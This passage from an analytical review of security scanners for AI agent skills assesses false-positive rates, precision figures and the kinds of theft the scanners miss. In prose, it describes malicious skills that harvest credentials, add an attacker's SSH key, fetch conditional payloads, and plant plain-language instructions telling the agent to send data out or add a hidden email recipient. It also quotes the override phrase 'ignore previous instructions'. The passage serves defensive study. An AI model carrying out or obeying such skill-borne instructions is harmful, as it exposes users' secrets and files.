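*Scientific Agent Skills* (2026), which describes a library of skills for research agents, shows how much of a scan report can come from API clients. A scan of the library's 163 skills produced 988 findings, 34 of them critical. Three rules produced 28 of the critical findings. Each of these rules fires when a skill both reads an environment variable and makes a network call, whether or not it sends the value it read.

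The critical findings fell on 11 skills, 8 of which name a credential-like variable in their own frontmatter. The library's maintainers say these rules systematically produce false positives when a skill reads its own key and calls its own service. In this report's terms, those findings are benign true positives. The maintainers are judging their own work, and a declared key shows only that the skill expects the key, not where the key goes. Still, their explanation is plausible for scientific databases that require an account. The counts also overstate the problem, since three rules respond to the same two facts and one ordinary client can receive several critical findings.

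Adding other methods to the static rules doesn't necessarily prevent false positives. *The Devil Wears Markdown* (2026) tests a system that combines static rules, test runs and language-model agents. The system wrongly classed 5 of 60 harmless skills as malicious, including `research-lookup`, which it flagged for using an API key and for an installation command that downloads and runs a script. The skill did contain both, but it needed the key for its normal work, and the command came from the vendor's documented setup. Running a remote script carries some risk because the vendor's server could later deliver something else. That is a reason to check the installer, but it isn't evidence that the skill's author is malicious.

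Tests on artificial skills can miss these false positives entirely. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) reports no false positives on 270 benign skills, but a program generated those skills to contain no malicious behaviour. According to the paper, real skills, which routinely start interpreters and use the network, would be a harder test.

Cloud tools can look more suspicious than simple API clients. Amazon Web Services, for example, usually identifies a caller by a signature. The client reads a secret key, combines it with the contents of the request through a hash function (a calculation that nobody can practically reverse), and sends the result, so the secret never leaves the machine. But the code still reads a credential, transforms it and sends something derived from it, and SkillsMetric gives its highest data-flow score to a chain with those three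 steps. Chen, Ji and colleagues use base64 encoding as their example of the middle step and don't say whether hashing also counts.

A deployment script may also copy the user's entire environment, which sounds like theft. Python lets a program specify the environment of another program that it starts, but the new list replaces the old one completely. To change one setting, the author copies everything and adds a line:

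```python
subprocess.run(["terraform", "apply"], env={**os.environ, "AWS_REGION": "eu-west-1"})
```

Terraform, a tool that sets up cloud servers, needs the keys as well as ordinary variables such as the search path for programs. A rule for bulk reads would correctly report this line. A reviewer can clear it by confirming that the command starts the real Terraform and that its configuration comes from the user.

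Telemetry, the usage data that a program reports to its maker, is harder to judge. A skill might ask during setup whether it may report errors and, if the user agrees, read an `ANALYTICS_KEY` and post error messages to an outside server. This code has both signals, and the server is unrelated to the service the user wanted. The user's consent makes the transfer legitimate, but the script is poor evidence of consent. A line that checks whether `TELEMETRY` equals `1` shows that the author included a setting for telemetry, but not that the user agreed to it.

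Attackers can disguise credential theft as telemetry, because telemetry looks ordinary. Liu and colleagues describe Flow Nexus, a workflow skill that searched the folders where SSH and cloud keys are kept, collected credentials from the environment and sent them to a fixed address that it presented as an "analytics" service. A reviewer who accepts every analytics call would accept this one. The data a script sends is a better guide than the server's name, because a legitimate error report doesn't require cloud keys.

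SkillSafe also flags Telegram, Discord and Slack addresses, a rule it added after finding a skill that sent the agent's observations to a configurable Telegram account. Many harmless skills exist to post messages, so SkillSafe rates the finding as medium and has its reviewing agent check whether SKILL.md declares the destination.

### Security tools

A security skill that teaches an agent to review code will contain examples of dangerous code, and a text rule will flag those examples. SkillSafe found that its rule for detecting reads of system files flagged checklists that told developers what to avoid. It now suppresses the finding if a nearby line contains words such as "avoid" or "vulnerable". An attacker can add those words too, so the exception is safest for text that neither the agent nor the computer will run.

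Other security tools really do what the rules describe, so the findings are benign true positives. A credential manager reads secrets, and a penetration-testing tool, which attacks a system with its owner's permission, connects to machines and runs commands on them.

Chen, Ji and colleagues scored 138,133 SKILL.md files with SkillsMetric and inspected the highest-scoring skills by hand. They found mostly legitimate security tools, including penetration-testing skills and antivirus scanners, and concluded that a high score reflects security-related content more than malice. They don't report how many skills they inspected.

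This finding is hard to reconcile with the same paper's proposal to block skills automatically from a score of about 45. Around 0.3 per cent of the skills, or roughly 400, scored that high. If the manual review is representative of these skills, the automatic block would mainly remove tools that security staff use.

Liu and colleagues found a similar result when they ran skills in tests. The test runs raised at least one alarm for 762 skills, and reviewers did not confirm 605 of these as malicious. Most of the 605 were harmless tools with security-related functions, such as penetration-testing utilities, credential managers and developer diagnostics. But in a sample from all 4,130 unconfirmed candidates, the reviewers classed only 4.9 per cent as legitimate security tools and 93.2 per cent as containing dormant triggers that the test runs had not set off. Security tools therefore seem much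 more common among skills that behave suspiciously when run than among all the skills that the text patterns select.

### Workloft's test of SkillSpector

In *A skill scanner flagged 15 of our 53 skills to delete*, Churchill (2026) reports a test on skills in daily use. His firm, Workloft, ran version 2.11.2 of NVIDIA's SkillSpector over its 53 installed skills in September 2026. Six were Workloft's own, and 47 came bundled with the tools the firm uses. SkillSpector rated 15 as safe, 23 as CAUTION and 15 as DO NOT INSTALL. Churchill reports 39 flagged skills, but his breakdown adds up to 38.

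Nearly all of the 15 skills marked DO NOT INSTALL were official vendor plugins. They included skills for creating other skills, writing commands and writing hooks, scripts that an agent runs automatically at certain moments. All six of Workloft's own skills passed.

Churchill describes only two findings in detail. One was a high-severity warning of prompt injection, an attack that hides instructions in text that an agent reads. The flagged line was a defence against such attacks, an instruction to treat a folder's name as plain text even if it was something like "ignore previous instructions". The warning was therefore a false positive, but it had nothing to do with network or credential code.

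In the other finding, SkillSpector reported data exfiltration in a plugin whose evaluation scripts read environment variables and started other programs. Churchill regards this as normal for evaluation scripts, which read their configuration, run a program and check the result. If he is right about the scripts' purpose, SkillSpector correctly detected the environment reads but wrongly reported them as exfiltration. He mentions no finding about a network import and doesn't break down the 38 warnings by category, so the test doesn't show how many came from the rules for network and environment code.

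The environment finding may not have decided any verdict either. Churchill doesn't say whether that plugin was among the 15. Under NVIDIA's published scoring, a single HIGH finding in a skill with scripts adds up to 32.5 points, which leads to CAUTION, so a DO NOT INSTALL verdict would have needed further findings.

Workloft ran only the static rules. NVIDIA also offers an optional stage in which a language model evaluates the skill, and it might have recognised that the skill was defending against prompt injection. Users can also record findings they have already accepted, so that later scans show only new ones. Recording benign true positives makes more sense than weakening the rule, since the same rule may correctly flag a problem in the next skill.

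One small firm selected the 53 skills, and many of the official plugins probably share authors and style, so the proportions may not hold elsewhere. Churchill reasonably treats official publication as good evidence that a plugin is harmless, but he doesn't report an audit of all 15. He also says that the scanner has high recall, but the test doesn't support this because it included no skill known to be malicious. The test does show that a firm would have lost a good part of its standard tools if it had let SkillSpector's static rules block installations.

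## How often are the warnings wrong?

Studies much larger than Workloft's test have estimated scanners' precision at anywhere from about 1 per cent to 99.6 per cent. The scanners differ in quality, but much of the spread comes from what each study counted as malicious and how many malicious skills it included.

### From 98,380 skills to 157

Liu, Chen and colleagues (2026) give the most detailed count in *Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild*, which covers the same study as *Do Not Mention This to the User*. They collected skills from two registries in January 2026 and narrowed them down in three steps.

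| Step | Skills | Share of the previous step | Share of all skills |
|---|---|---|---|
| Collected | 98,380 | | 100% |
| Matched at least one static pattern | 4,287 | 4.4% | 4.4% |
| Showed a suspicious sign in a test run | 762 | 17.8% | 0.77% |
| Confirmed as malicious by two reviewers | 157 | 20.6% | 0.16% |

Rejecting every skill with a pattern match would have excluded 4,287 skills. The reviewers confirmed the warnings for 157 of them, or 3.7 per cent. One publisher wrote 85 of the 157 from a single template, each posing as a different brand. Without that publisher's skills, the confirmed share is 72 of 4,202, or 1.7 per cent.

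The 3.7 per cent covers all 14 patterns together, including some for instructions in SKILL.md that a language model helped to find, so it is not the precision of the network and credential rules. Among the 157 confirmed skills, 101 contained credential harvesting (E2) and 79 contained external transmission (E1). Liu and colleagues give no such breakdown for the 4,287 candidates, so readers cannot calculate how many harmless skills each rule flagged.

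They also report that Cisco's scanner rated 10.7 per cent of skills CRITICAL, with a precision of at most 1.1 per cent, assuming that it caught every malicious skill. These figures are inconsistent. If the 10.7 per cent refers to the same collection, the scanner flagged 10,527 skills, and the 157 malicious ones would be 1.5 per cent of them. A precision of 1.1 per cent would require about 14,300 flagged skills. Perhaps the lower figure also counts skills rated HIGH, since Cisco's `is_safe` property fails at either level, but the paper doesn't explain the difference. Its claim of a 150-fold improvement over static analysis alone implies a third figure for static precision, about 0.7 per cent.

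The difference between 1.1 and 1.5 per cent hardly matters to a user. The assumption of perfect recall matters more, because *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* measured a recall of 36.1 per cent for the static mode of Cisco's scanner on a different set of skills. At that recall, the scanner would have caught 57 of the 157, and its precision would be about 0.5 per cent.

### What the 99.6 per cent measures

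Liu and colleagues report 99.6 per cent for their full method, but their test was much too easy. They drew its 150 harmless skills from the 94,093 that had matched no static pattern, which left out the API clients, credential managers and penetration-testing tools that trigger the rules. Two researchers checked each harmless skill, and the team replaced 12 they disagreed on, which removed some borderline cases too.

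The method also runs only the skills that match a static pattern, so a harmless skill that matches none can't become a false positive, however badly the later steps work. The 150 malicious skills came from the 157 that the same method had already confirmed, so the test mostly checks whether the method reproduces its own earlier results.

The published precision of 99.6 per cent looks wrong. Liu and colleagues split the 300 skills into five parts of 60 and report an average of 0.6 false positives per part. If each part contained 30 malicious skills and the method caught them all, its precision was 30 out of 30.6, or 98 per cent. The published figure may come from combining the average false positives for one part with the 150 malicious skills in all five, since 150 out of 150.6 is 99.6 per cent.

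The counts in the table give a more useful measure, the precision of the automatic part of the method. Static patterns and test runs together selected 762 skills, and human reviewers confirmed 157 of them, or about 21 per cent.

Liu and colleagues reported 157 skills and point out that the registries eventually removed them all. This is some support for their labels, but a registry has little reason to keep an unknown author's skill after security researchers warn about it. *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* re-examined the 157 skills and judged 95 malicious and 34 benign. It put the other 28 into two intermediate classes: "risky" for potentially harmful behaviour with a legitimate purpose, and "suspicious" for content whose intent was unclear.

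### 3.7 per cent or 95 per cent?

The 4,130 flagged skills that Liu and colleagues did not confirm are a much larger source of uncertainty. Two researchers reviewed a random tenth of them, 413 skills. They classed 93.2 per cent as "dormant malware", whose triggers, such as a later date or the name of a production server, had not occurred during a 60-second test run. They considered 1.9 per cent to be attacks that the test runs had missed, and only 4.9 per cent to be legitimate security tools.

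If these proportions hold for all 4,130, the unconfirmed skills include about 3,849 with dormant malware and 78 missed attacks. Together with the 157, that makes roughly 4,085 malicious skills. The same static patterns on the same skills then have very different precision, depending on which labels one accepts:

| Skills counted as malicious | Number | Precision of the static patterns | Base rate |
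|---|---|---|---|
| Those that the second review accepted | 95 | 2.2% | 0.10% |
| Those that Liu and colleagues confirmed | 157 | 3.7% | 0.16% |
| Confirmed skills and missed attacks | about 235 | 5.5% | 0.24% |
| All of these and dormant malware | about 4,085 | 95% | 4.2% |

The 95 per cent is hard to believe. The sample has no category for ordinary harmless programs, although the E2 pattern printed in the paper matches any Python script that reads its own API key in the usual way. The figures also conflict with the paper's statement that most of the 605 unconfirmed skills that raised alarms in test runs were benign tools. That would be at least 303 skills, but the sample implies only about 200 legitimate tools among all 4,130. Chance could just about explain this gap in a sample of 413.

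Code described as "dormant" may not be malicious. Plenty of legitimate code waits for a condition, such as a deployment script that acts only on the production server. Finding such a branch shows that the test didn't run some of the code, but not that the code is malware. The true precision is probably much closer to 3.7 per cent than to 95 per cent, but the published descriptions don't establish this.

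This affects every precision figure that relies on the 157. Cisco's supposed maximum of 1.1 per cent holds only if the unconfirmed skills are harmless. If all 4,085 were malicious and Cisco's scanner had rated every one CRITICAL, its precision would be 39 per cent.

Scanners and studies may also measure different things. *Beyond Maliciousness* (2026) separates an author's intent from the harm that a skill's access makes possible, since a skill written without malice can still have far more authority than it needs. A warning about such a skill identifies a real risk, but a study that counts only malicious intent will record the warning as a false positive.

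### What the base rate does to precision

Suppose everyone agreed on the labels. Precision would still depend on the base rate, along with recall and the false-positive rate, the share of harmless skills that the scanner flags:

```
                        recall × base rate
precision = ---------------------------------------------------------------
            recall × base rate + false-positive rate × (1 − base rate)
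```

Chen, Ji and colleagues tested SkillsMetric on 266 malicious and 2,000 harmless skills and report 63.4 per cent precision and 62.4 per cent recall. That means 166 of the 262 skills it flagged were malicious and 96 were harmless, so its false-positive rate was 4.8 per cent (96 out of 2,000).

If 0.16 per cent of 100,000 skills were malicious, SkillsMetric would, at the same rates, catch 100 of the 160 malicious skills and wrongly flag about 4,790 of the 99,840 harmless ones. Its precision would be 2 per cent. For half its warnings to be right, the false-positive rate would have to fall to 0.1 per cent, or one harmless skill in a thousand.

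Estimates of the base rate vary widely, even for a single registry. Koi's first audit put it at 11.9 per cent for ClawHub. *Technical Report* (2026), a study of threats from agent skills, describes 76 malicious skills on ClawHub that its researchers confirmed by hand. *MalSkillBench* (Guo, Jia and colleagues, 2026) puts the total at 3,984 skills, which makes the base rate 1.9 per cent. The figure of 76 is a minimum, because the researchers had no time to review every flagged skill, but it also includes each republished copy separately. Copies can make up most of such a count. Guo and colleagues collected 703 malicious skills from public sources, and only 193 remained after the *Demystifying* team removed duplicates.

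The next table applies the formula at these three base rates. SkillsMetric's figures come from its own test, and the others come from *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs*, where 60 per cent of the 1,477 test skills were malicious. The first four scanners use only static analysis, while skill-vetter has a language model inspect the files.

| Scanner | Recall | False-positive rate | Precision in its test | Precision at 11.9% | Precision at 1.9% | Precision at 0.16% |
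|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| SkillsMetric | 62.4% | 4.8% | 63.4% | 64% | 20% | 2.0% |
| Cisco, static mode | 36.1% | 12.0% | 81.8% | 29% | 5.5% | 0.5% |
| SkillSpector, static mode | 52.0% | 17.3% | 81.9% | 29% | 5.5% | 0.5% |
| skillscan-security | 85.1% | 50.4% | 70.4% | 19% | 3.2% | 0.3% |
| skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 | 93.0% | 6.3% | 95.7% | 67% | 22% | 2.3% |

SkillsMetric has the lowest precision in its own test, yet it ranks second whenever the tools are compared at the same base rate of malicious skills. The tests used different skills, so this isn't a fair ranking, but it shows that comparing published precision figures directly is misleading. Cisco and SkillSpector reach 82 per cent precision mainly because most of the test skills were malicious.

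ClawHub's own rule engine had the highest measured precision in the same tests, at 100 per cent, because it blocked none of the 591 harmless skills, though it caught only 7.4 per cent of the malicious ones. But 591 skills are too few to rule out a false-positive rate of about 0.5 per cent. At that rate, precision would be only about 2 per cent if 0.16 per cent of skills are malicious.

Chen, Ji and colleagues report a second precision figure for SkillsMetric, 89.4 per cent, from cross-validation (repeated tests on different parts of the data). Recall was almost unchanged at 62.2 per cent. For 2,000 harmless skills, these figures imply only about 20 false positives, compared with 96 in the single run. The paper doesn't explain the difference. Cross-validation may have used only roughly 400 harmless skills, which would give the higher precision with the same error rates as the single run, but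 that is only a guess. Even with only 20 false positives per 2,000 harmless skills, precision would be about 9 per cent at a base rate of 0.16 per cent.

The 4.8 per cent false-positive rate may also be too low for skills that contain code. SkillsMetric flagged 1.75 per cent of real skills when it scanned only their SKILL.md files. If it flagged the 1,600 harmless test skills without scripts at the same rate, they would account for 28 of the 96 false positives. The other 68 would come from the 400 skills with scripts, a rate of 17 per cent. This estimate is rough, but probably closer to what the user of an API client would experience.

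### Scans of whole registries

Across a whole registry, a scanner's precision can be no higher than the base rate of malicious skills divided by the share of skills it flags. It reaches this limit only if it catches every malicious skill.

*Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* reports that SkillSpector rated 45.8 per cent of 84,560 ClawHub skills DO NOT INSTALL. If 1.9 per cent of the registry is malicious, at most 4 per cent of those warnings are right. If the share is 11.9 per cent, as in Koi's first audit, the limit is 26 per cent.

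These results also suggest that the test sets are too easy. In tests, SkillSpector's static mode flagged 17.3 per cent of harmless skills and 52.0 per cent of malicious ones. For those rates to produce the 45.8 per cent flagged on ClawHub, 82 per cent of the registry would have to be malicious. Even with the language model that made SkillSpector flag the most skills, about a third would have to be malicious. ClawHub may use another version or other settings, but it is more likely that real harmless skills trigger more rules than the ones in the tests. If so, the precision figures in the table above are too high.

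*Context Matters* (Holzbauer, Schmidt and colleagues, 2026) reports that the marketplaces' own scans flagged 46.8 per cent of skills on ClawHub, 23.0 per cent on skills.sh and 6.0 per cent on SkillsDirectory. The registries hold different skills but also use different scanners, so these percentages are a poor guide to which registry is safest.

Holzbauer and colleagues then compared flagged skills with the GitHub projects that contained them. They checked whether each project's documentation and code matched the skill's description, and considered the project's age, activity and popularity. Of 2,887 flagged skill-project pairs, only 15, or 0.52 per cent, still looked suspicious.

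The other 99.48 per cent were not necessarily false alarms. Holzbauer and colleagues describe their score as an aid to triage, not a judgement of malice, and a careful thief can publish a project that matches a malicious skill. They could also check only skills that had a GitHub project for comparison. But the result suggests that many flagged skills do what one would expect from the software around them.

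*Agent Skills in the Wild* (January 2026), an earlier study by Liu and other co-authors, found a security vulnerability in 26.1 per cent of 31,132 skills, according to Holzbauer and colleagues. The skills came from skills.rest and skillsmp.com, the two registries where Liu and colleagues later confirmed 0.16 per cent of skills as malicious. The two figures are compatible because a vulnerability can be an honest developer's mistake. Reading the 26.1 per cent as the share of malicious skills would exaggerate the problem by a factor of about 160.

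*MalSkills* (2026) provides the best evidence here that a scanner can search a large registry without giving reviewers too many harmless skills to check. Its detector flagged only 620 of roughly 150,000 public skills. Two of the paper's authors reviewed all 620, with a third settling disagreements, and confirmed 400 as malicious. That is a precision of 65 per cent, and it implies a false-positive rate of about 0.15 per cent, far below any non-zero rate in the table. However, the reviewers were judging their own tool, the registries had not yet confirmed the reports, and the scan doesn't measure how many malicious skills the detector missed.

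PyPI, the public registry of Python packages, had similar attacks before agent skills existed. Liu and colleagues cite a 2023 study of 4,669 malicious PyPI packages, about 75 per cent of which had reached users' projects. Guo and colleagues describe a package called `pyconau-funtimes` with a reverse shell, code that gives an attacker a command line on the victim's machine. They found the same code in a skill called `math-calculator`, with only the attacker's address changed. This overlap is a reason to try package scanners on skills. Guo and colleagues tested such scanners, along with prompt-injection detectors, on 4,000 harmless skills. The noisiest tool flagged 3,979 of them, so its warnings don't help users tell malicious skills from harmless ones.

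### The highest-scoring skills from eight scanners

A reviewer with limited time would probably start with the skills that look worst. ramimac.me's *Claude Code Skills Scanner Benchmark* tests how well that works with eight scanners, using only their pattern rules and turning off any language-model stages. Each skill received 4 points for a critical finding, 3 for a high, 2 for a medium and 1 for a low. The five highest-scoring skills from each scanner gave 40 results for 35 different skills, and AI agents judged each result by reading the skill's SKILL.md.

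None of the 40 results was a malicious skill. The page's summary lists 31 benign true positives and 9 false positives, but the labels beside the individual results add up to 35 and 5. Some labels are also debatable. For example, a skill for managing a portfolio on the Kraken cryptocurrency exchange is labeled a false positive because its findings came from financial keywords and the handling of API credentials. But the credential findings, at least, seem to describe the code correctly, which would make them benign true positives.

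The 40 results aren't representative of all warnings. Adding up points favours large skills with many matches, and one skill had 3,255 findings. At least 12 of the 40 results were security tools, and the five results from Cisco's scanner were all versions of one self-improvement skill called Evolver. The AI agents read SKILL.md, so they may also have missed malicious code in a script.

The same page reports results for three skills from a known trojan campaign. A scanner called agentvet detected all three, while Cisco's scanner missed them all and gave its highest scores to a harmless skill and its copies. A high total score therefore seems to be a poor reason to read one skill before another.

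### How much one finding tells the reviewer

Most of these studies measure verdicts on whole skills, but *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* also reports some figures for individual findings. It examined up to three findings for each harmless skill that a scanner had blocked. In the static modes of Cisco's scanner, SkillSpector and skillscan-security, 373 of 775 such findings (48 per cent) concerned access to credentials or local state. This category is broader than environment variables, since it also includes configuration files and a skill's own saved data. It was the largest category for SkillSpector and skillscan-security, and one finding behind the largest for Cisco's scanner.

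In the study, the skillscan-security scanner reported undeclared network use, a medium-severity finding, in 48.3 per cent of malicious skills and 29.3 per cent of harmless ones. The finding is therefore 1.65 times as common in malicious skills, which makes it weak evidence of malice. If 0.16 per cent of all skills are malicious, or 1 in 625, then about 1 in 380 skills with the finding are malicious. At Koi's base rate of 11.9 per cent, the finding raises the probability that a skill is malicious to 18 per cent.

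## What real theft do these rules miss?

### Ordinary code that no rule matches

A text pattern can miss theft code even when the code isn't disguised. E1, the external-transmission rule from Liu and colleagues, misses any request, malicious or legitimate, whose web address is in a variable. The printed rule also covers only one Python library, `requests`, so it doesn't flag a script that sends a key with `httpx`. Real scanners have longer lists, but those are also incomplete.

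*Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* shows how common such gaps are. For each malicious test skill that any of four static scanners failed to block, the study compared that scanner's report with the harmful part of the skill. A skill that three scanners missed counts three times.

| Why the scanner did not block the skill | All four scanners | Without ClawHub's own engine |
|---|---|---|
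| No rule matched the harmful code | 1,120 (58%) | 492 (44%) |
| The attack was in plain language | 482 (25%) | 308 (28%) |
| The scanner reported the behaviour but rated it too low | 310 (16%) | 300 (27%) |
| Wrong labels and other cases | 23 (1%) | 15 (1%) |

One of the test skills looked up the weather and also added an SSH key to the list of keys that can log in to the machine. The added key lets the attacker log in later and take whatever is there. Rules for network imports and environment reads don't catch this, because adding the key neither reads a secret nor sends one. SkillSpector has a rule for it, but Cisco's scanner had none.

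In the third row, the report contained the evidence but the verdict was still clean. For example, a test skill uploaded customer data, and skillscan-security reported undeclared network access at medium severity, which isn't enough to block a skill. Someone could still catch this theft by reading the findings, but would install the skill if they checked only the verdict.

Longer lists and stricter thresholds catch more theft, but they also flag more harmless code. *The Devil Wears Markdown* counted the alerts from Cisco's scanner instead of using its verdict, with a cut-off chosen on a separate set of skills. This caught 73 of 80 malicious skills (91 per cent), compared with 36.1 per cent for the scanner's static verdict in the *Demystifying* tests. The two studies used different skills, so the threshold may not explain the whole difference. Counting alerts also flagged 33 of 60 harmless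 skills, and the median number of alerts was one for both malicious and harmless skills. *MaliciousSkillBench* (2026) found the same trade-off. A scanner with few false positives could have very low recall, while a more sensitive one flagged many harmless skills.

### Theft without the two signals

A rule that requires both credential harvesting and external transmission would miss any theft that doesn't show both, even if it detected every instance of each. Liu and colleagues labelled 157 malicious skills by hand and found both in 58, only harvesting in 43, only transmission in 21, and neither in 35. The rule would therefore miss 99 of the 157, or 63 per cent.

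Some of these skills download a program to do part of the work. Of the 85 skills from the largest publisher, 83 combined credential harvesting with a command that fetches and runs a remote script.

Secrets are also often stored in files. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) describes skills that direct the agent to credential files in predictable places. It also cites a campaign, reported by Zenity Labs in July 2026, that targeted cloud tokens, package manager credentials, container settings and project environment files. Liu and colleagues have a separate rule for credential files, and they labelled 17 such reads and 112 cases of credential harvesting from the environment. But a file rule depends on a list of known paths, so it misses the theft of data that can be anywhere, such as a customer list or source code.

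A skill can also send data without a network library. The Polymarket backdoors on ClawHub used `curl`, and other programs on a user's computer can transfer files. An import rule detects at most a library for starting programs, which legitimate scripts routinely use.

Some skills send data out through the agent's own connections. Liu and colleagues describe Lark Agent, a skill whose configuration file already contained API credentials and connected the user's agent to the attacker's workspace. Anything the agent stored there during its normal work would have gone to the attacker. Another skill, Hooks Automation, used Claude Code's hooks to watch the agent's every action and send the results to outside servers. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* points out that such transfers use the same channels as legitimate ones, so only purpose-built monitoring can tell them apart.

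A script can expose a key without sending anything. If it prints the key, for example in a debugging message, the key enters the model's context, where a later prompt injection could extract it. Chen and colleagues attribute 73.5 per cent of the issues in their study of leaked credentials to this pattern. Most of the leaks they found were developers' mistakes, so the pattern is usually a weakness that a thief could exploit rather than theft itself.

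A rule for printed secrets would mostly produce false positives, though. *Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills* (2026) searched roughly 48,700 skills for code that might print a credential. It checked all 433 skills with the clearest evidence and found that only 22 printed a real secret. The others printed things like host names, file paths or masked keys. In a sample from a further 652 skills, about 11 per cent were real leaks, which suggests around 70 more in that group.

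### Code outside the scan

Most scanners read only the files in the skill's folder, but a script also runs the code of every package it imports. If one of those packages steals keys, the skill's own files may contain nothing suspicious except the package's name. SkillSpector looks up listed packages in a database of known vulnerabilities, but this does not help detect a malicious package that nobody has reported yet.

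Dependencies can also pass through several skills. *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* cites a study of more than 1.43 million skills that found hidden package dependencies and known malicious skills that other skills still depended on. One of the paper's own test cases was a setup script that changed where the computer gets its packages. The script stole nothing itself, but it let whoever controlled the new source supply altered packages later.

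Scanners also skip some files in the folder or read them only partly. Images, archives, office documents, compiled programs and bundled machine-learning models can all contain instructions or code, so a scanner that ignores them may miss an attack. But treating every unreadable file as a threat will block harmless skills. Cisco's scanner reports low coverage as a high-severity problem, and this rule caused some of its false positives in the *Demystifying* tests.

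Liu and colleagues found disguised code in only 15 of their 157 malicious skills. The number may be low partly because they ran only skills that had already matched a pattern, and well-disguised code is less likely to match one.

Content that a skill fetches after the scan is harder to catch. The scanner can detect the command and the address, but not what the server will send later. Fetching remote content was the most common pattern in the study by Liu and colleagues, with 159 of the 632 vulnerabilities they labelled. A skill called Stealth Ops downloaded its second program only under certain conditions, such as administrator rights, a production server's name or a time outside working hours. Scanning the downloaded file doesn't fully solve the problem, because the server can send a different file to the next visitor.

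### Detection rates by type of attack

Chen, Ji and colleagues tested SkillsMetric on 16 types of attack, and the results varied widely by type. The table shows the types closest to credential theft, with 95 per cent confidence intervals calculated from their counts.

| Type of attack | Caught | Detection rate | Confidence interval |
|---|---|---|---|
| Data exfiltration | 26 of 28 | 92.9% | 77–98% |
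| Hidden data (steganography) | 26 of 28 | 92.9% | 77–98% |
| Encoded payload | 13 of 29 | 44.8% | 28–62% |
| Prompt injection | 5 of 12 | 41.7% | 19–68% |
| Remote script | 8 of 29 | 27.6% | 15–46% |

SkillsMetric detects theft well when all the steps are in the skill's code, because a complete data-flow chain is enough to flag a skill. If a remote script does the stealing, the skill contains only the code that downloads it. Encoding hides the words that text patterns match, and the stage that detects unusual bytes has too little weight on its own to flag an encoded payload.

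The prompt injection figure overstates how well SkillsMetric catches attacks written in plain language. According to Chen, Ji and colleagues, the injections it caught contained blocks of code, which triggered the text patterns. The test therefore gives no example of SkillsMetric catching an injection written entirely in prose.

These attacks were also mostly artificial. Chen, Ji and colleagues acknowledge that a determined attacker might disguise the code better, so the 92.9 per cent figure for data exfiltration may be too high for real theft.

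### Theft by plain instruction

The largest gap is theft that needs no script. A SKILL.md file can contain instructions, written in ordinary prose, for the agent to read a key or a document and include it in a message. The agent does this with its own tools, so the skill contains no network imports or code that reads environment variables for the rules to flag.

Liu and colleagues found an email skill that told the agent to add the attacker's address as a hidden recipient, without asking the user or mentioning it. The theft involved no credential, and the emails went out from the user's own account.

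Static scanners are very weak at catching attacks written in natural language. One test set in *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* has 93 malicious skills that mostly express their attacks this way. Cisco's static mode caught 7 of them and SkillSpector's caught 11. In the study's overall count, missing code rules caused more misses than natural language did, but that depends on which attacks the test sets contain. Programmers can write the missing code rules, but it is much harder to write a pattern for every way of asking an agent to send a file.

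Rules for suspicious phrases have the same problem as rules for imports. The email skill told the agent not to ask the user. A scanner blocked a harmless skill in the *Demystifying* tests because it also told the agent not to ask for permission, but only so that the agent would continue to the next phase of a task.

### How much of the threat is in SKILL.md?

Liu and colleagues found 532 of their 632 labelled vulnerabilities (84.2 per cent) in SKILL.md files, 8.5 per cent in executable code, and the remaining 7.3 per cent in configuration files and other sources. They conclude that static analysis of code misses the main attack surface.

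However, the 84.2 per cent counts all vulnerabilities found in SKILL.md files, whether in prose or in code. These files can contain shell commands, which a text rule can match. Only 209 of the 632 vulnerabilities belonged to the four patterns for instructions and manipulation of the agent. Even if all 209 were in SKILL.md files, another 323 vulnerabilities in those files were of other kinds, such as downloading and running a script. A scanner that reads only script files would miss them, but one that also applies its code rules to SKILL.md could catch many.

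The publisher behind 85 of the 157 malicious skills (54.1 per cent) strongly affects the share of vulnerabilities found in SKILL.md, because its skills contained 370 of the 632. Even if all 370 were in SKILL.md, at least 162 of the 262 vulnerabilities from other publishers (62 per cent) were there too.

Chen, Ji and colleagues say the opposite, that malicious logic is typically in scripts, but they give no count. Liu and colleagues provide better evidence because they give figures, although they counted vulnerabilities, and one skill can contain many.

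The mix of attacks in any collection depends heavily on a few attackers, so a scanner can look excellent because it recognises one large campaign. Guo and colleagues collected 703 real malicious skills, 81 per cent of them published by two accounts. In 86.3 per cent of the 703, the skill claimed to need an extra program that was really malware. VirusTotal, which checks files with many antivirus engines, ranked at the top on these skills alone but near the bottom on the full benchmark, which also included generated attacks of many other kinds. The best skill scanner Guo and colleagues tested caught 98.4 per cent of attacks in code but did badly on prompt injection.

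Some attacks depend on both a skill's instructions and its code. *From Instructions to Exploits* (2026) describes a presentation skill whose instructions tell the agent to run a backup script whenever it creates a file. The instruction looks like routine caution, and a script that uploads backups can be legitimate, but together they send the user's presentation to a stranger. Liu and colleagues found a very similar skill in a public registry. It was a copy of a legitimate presentation skill, with three lines added to its 484 lines of instructions and a script that uploaded the files.

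Chen and colleagues found that 76.3 per cent of the credential leaks they studied involved both the instructions and the code. In some, the instructions tell the agent to pass the user's credentials to a function, which forwards them to an undeclared address. The script may never read an environment variable, because the agent supplies the credentials.

### How much is a clean report worth?

*AgentTrap* (Zhuang, Xing and colleagues, 2026) tested six scanners on 91 malicious tasks and 50 harmless ones, each with a skill installed. Two of the scanners, SkillScan and MalBench, follow methods from studies by Liu and co-authors. The last column shows how likely a skill is to be malicious when the scanner doesn't flag it, assuming that 11.9 per cent of skills in the registry are malicious, as in Koi's first audit of ClawHub.

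| Scanner | Malicious tasks flagged | Harmless tasks flagged | Risk after a clean report |
|---|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal | 0 of 91 | 0 of 50 | 11.9% |
| Cisco, static mode | 26 of 91 | 5 of 50 | 9.7% |
| MalBench, rules only | 31 of 91 | 7 of 50 | 9.4% |
| MalBench with a language model | 44 of 91 | 3 of 50 | 6.9% |
| SkillScan with a language model | 50 of 91 | 4 of 50 | 6.2% |
| AgentTrap's own language-model review | 80 of 91 | 2 of 50 | 1.7% |

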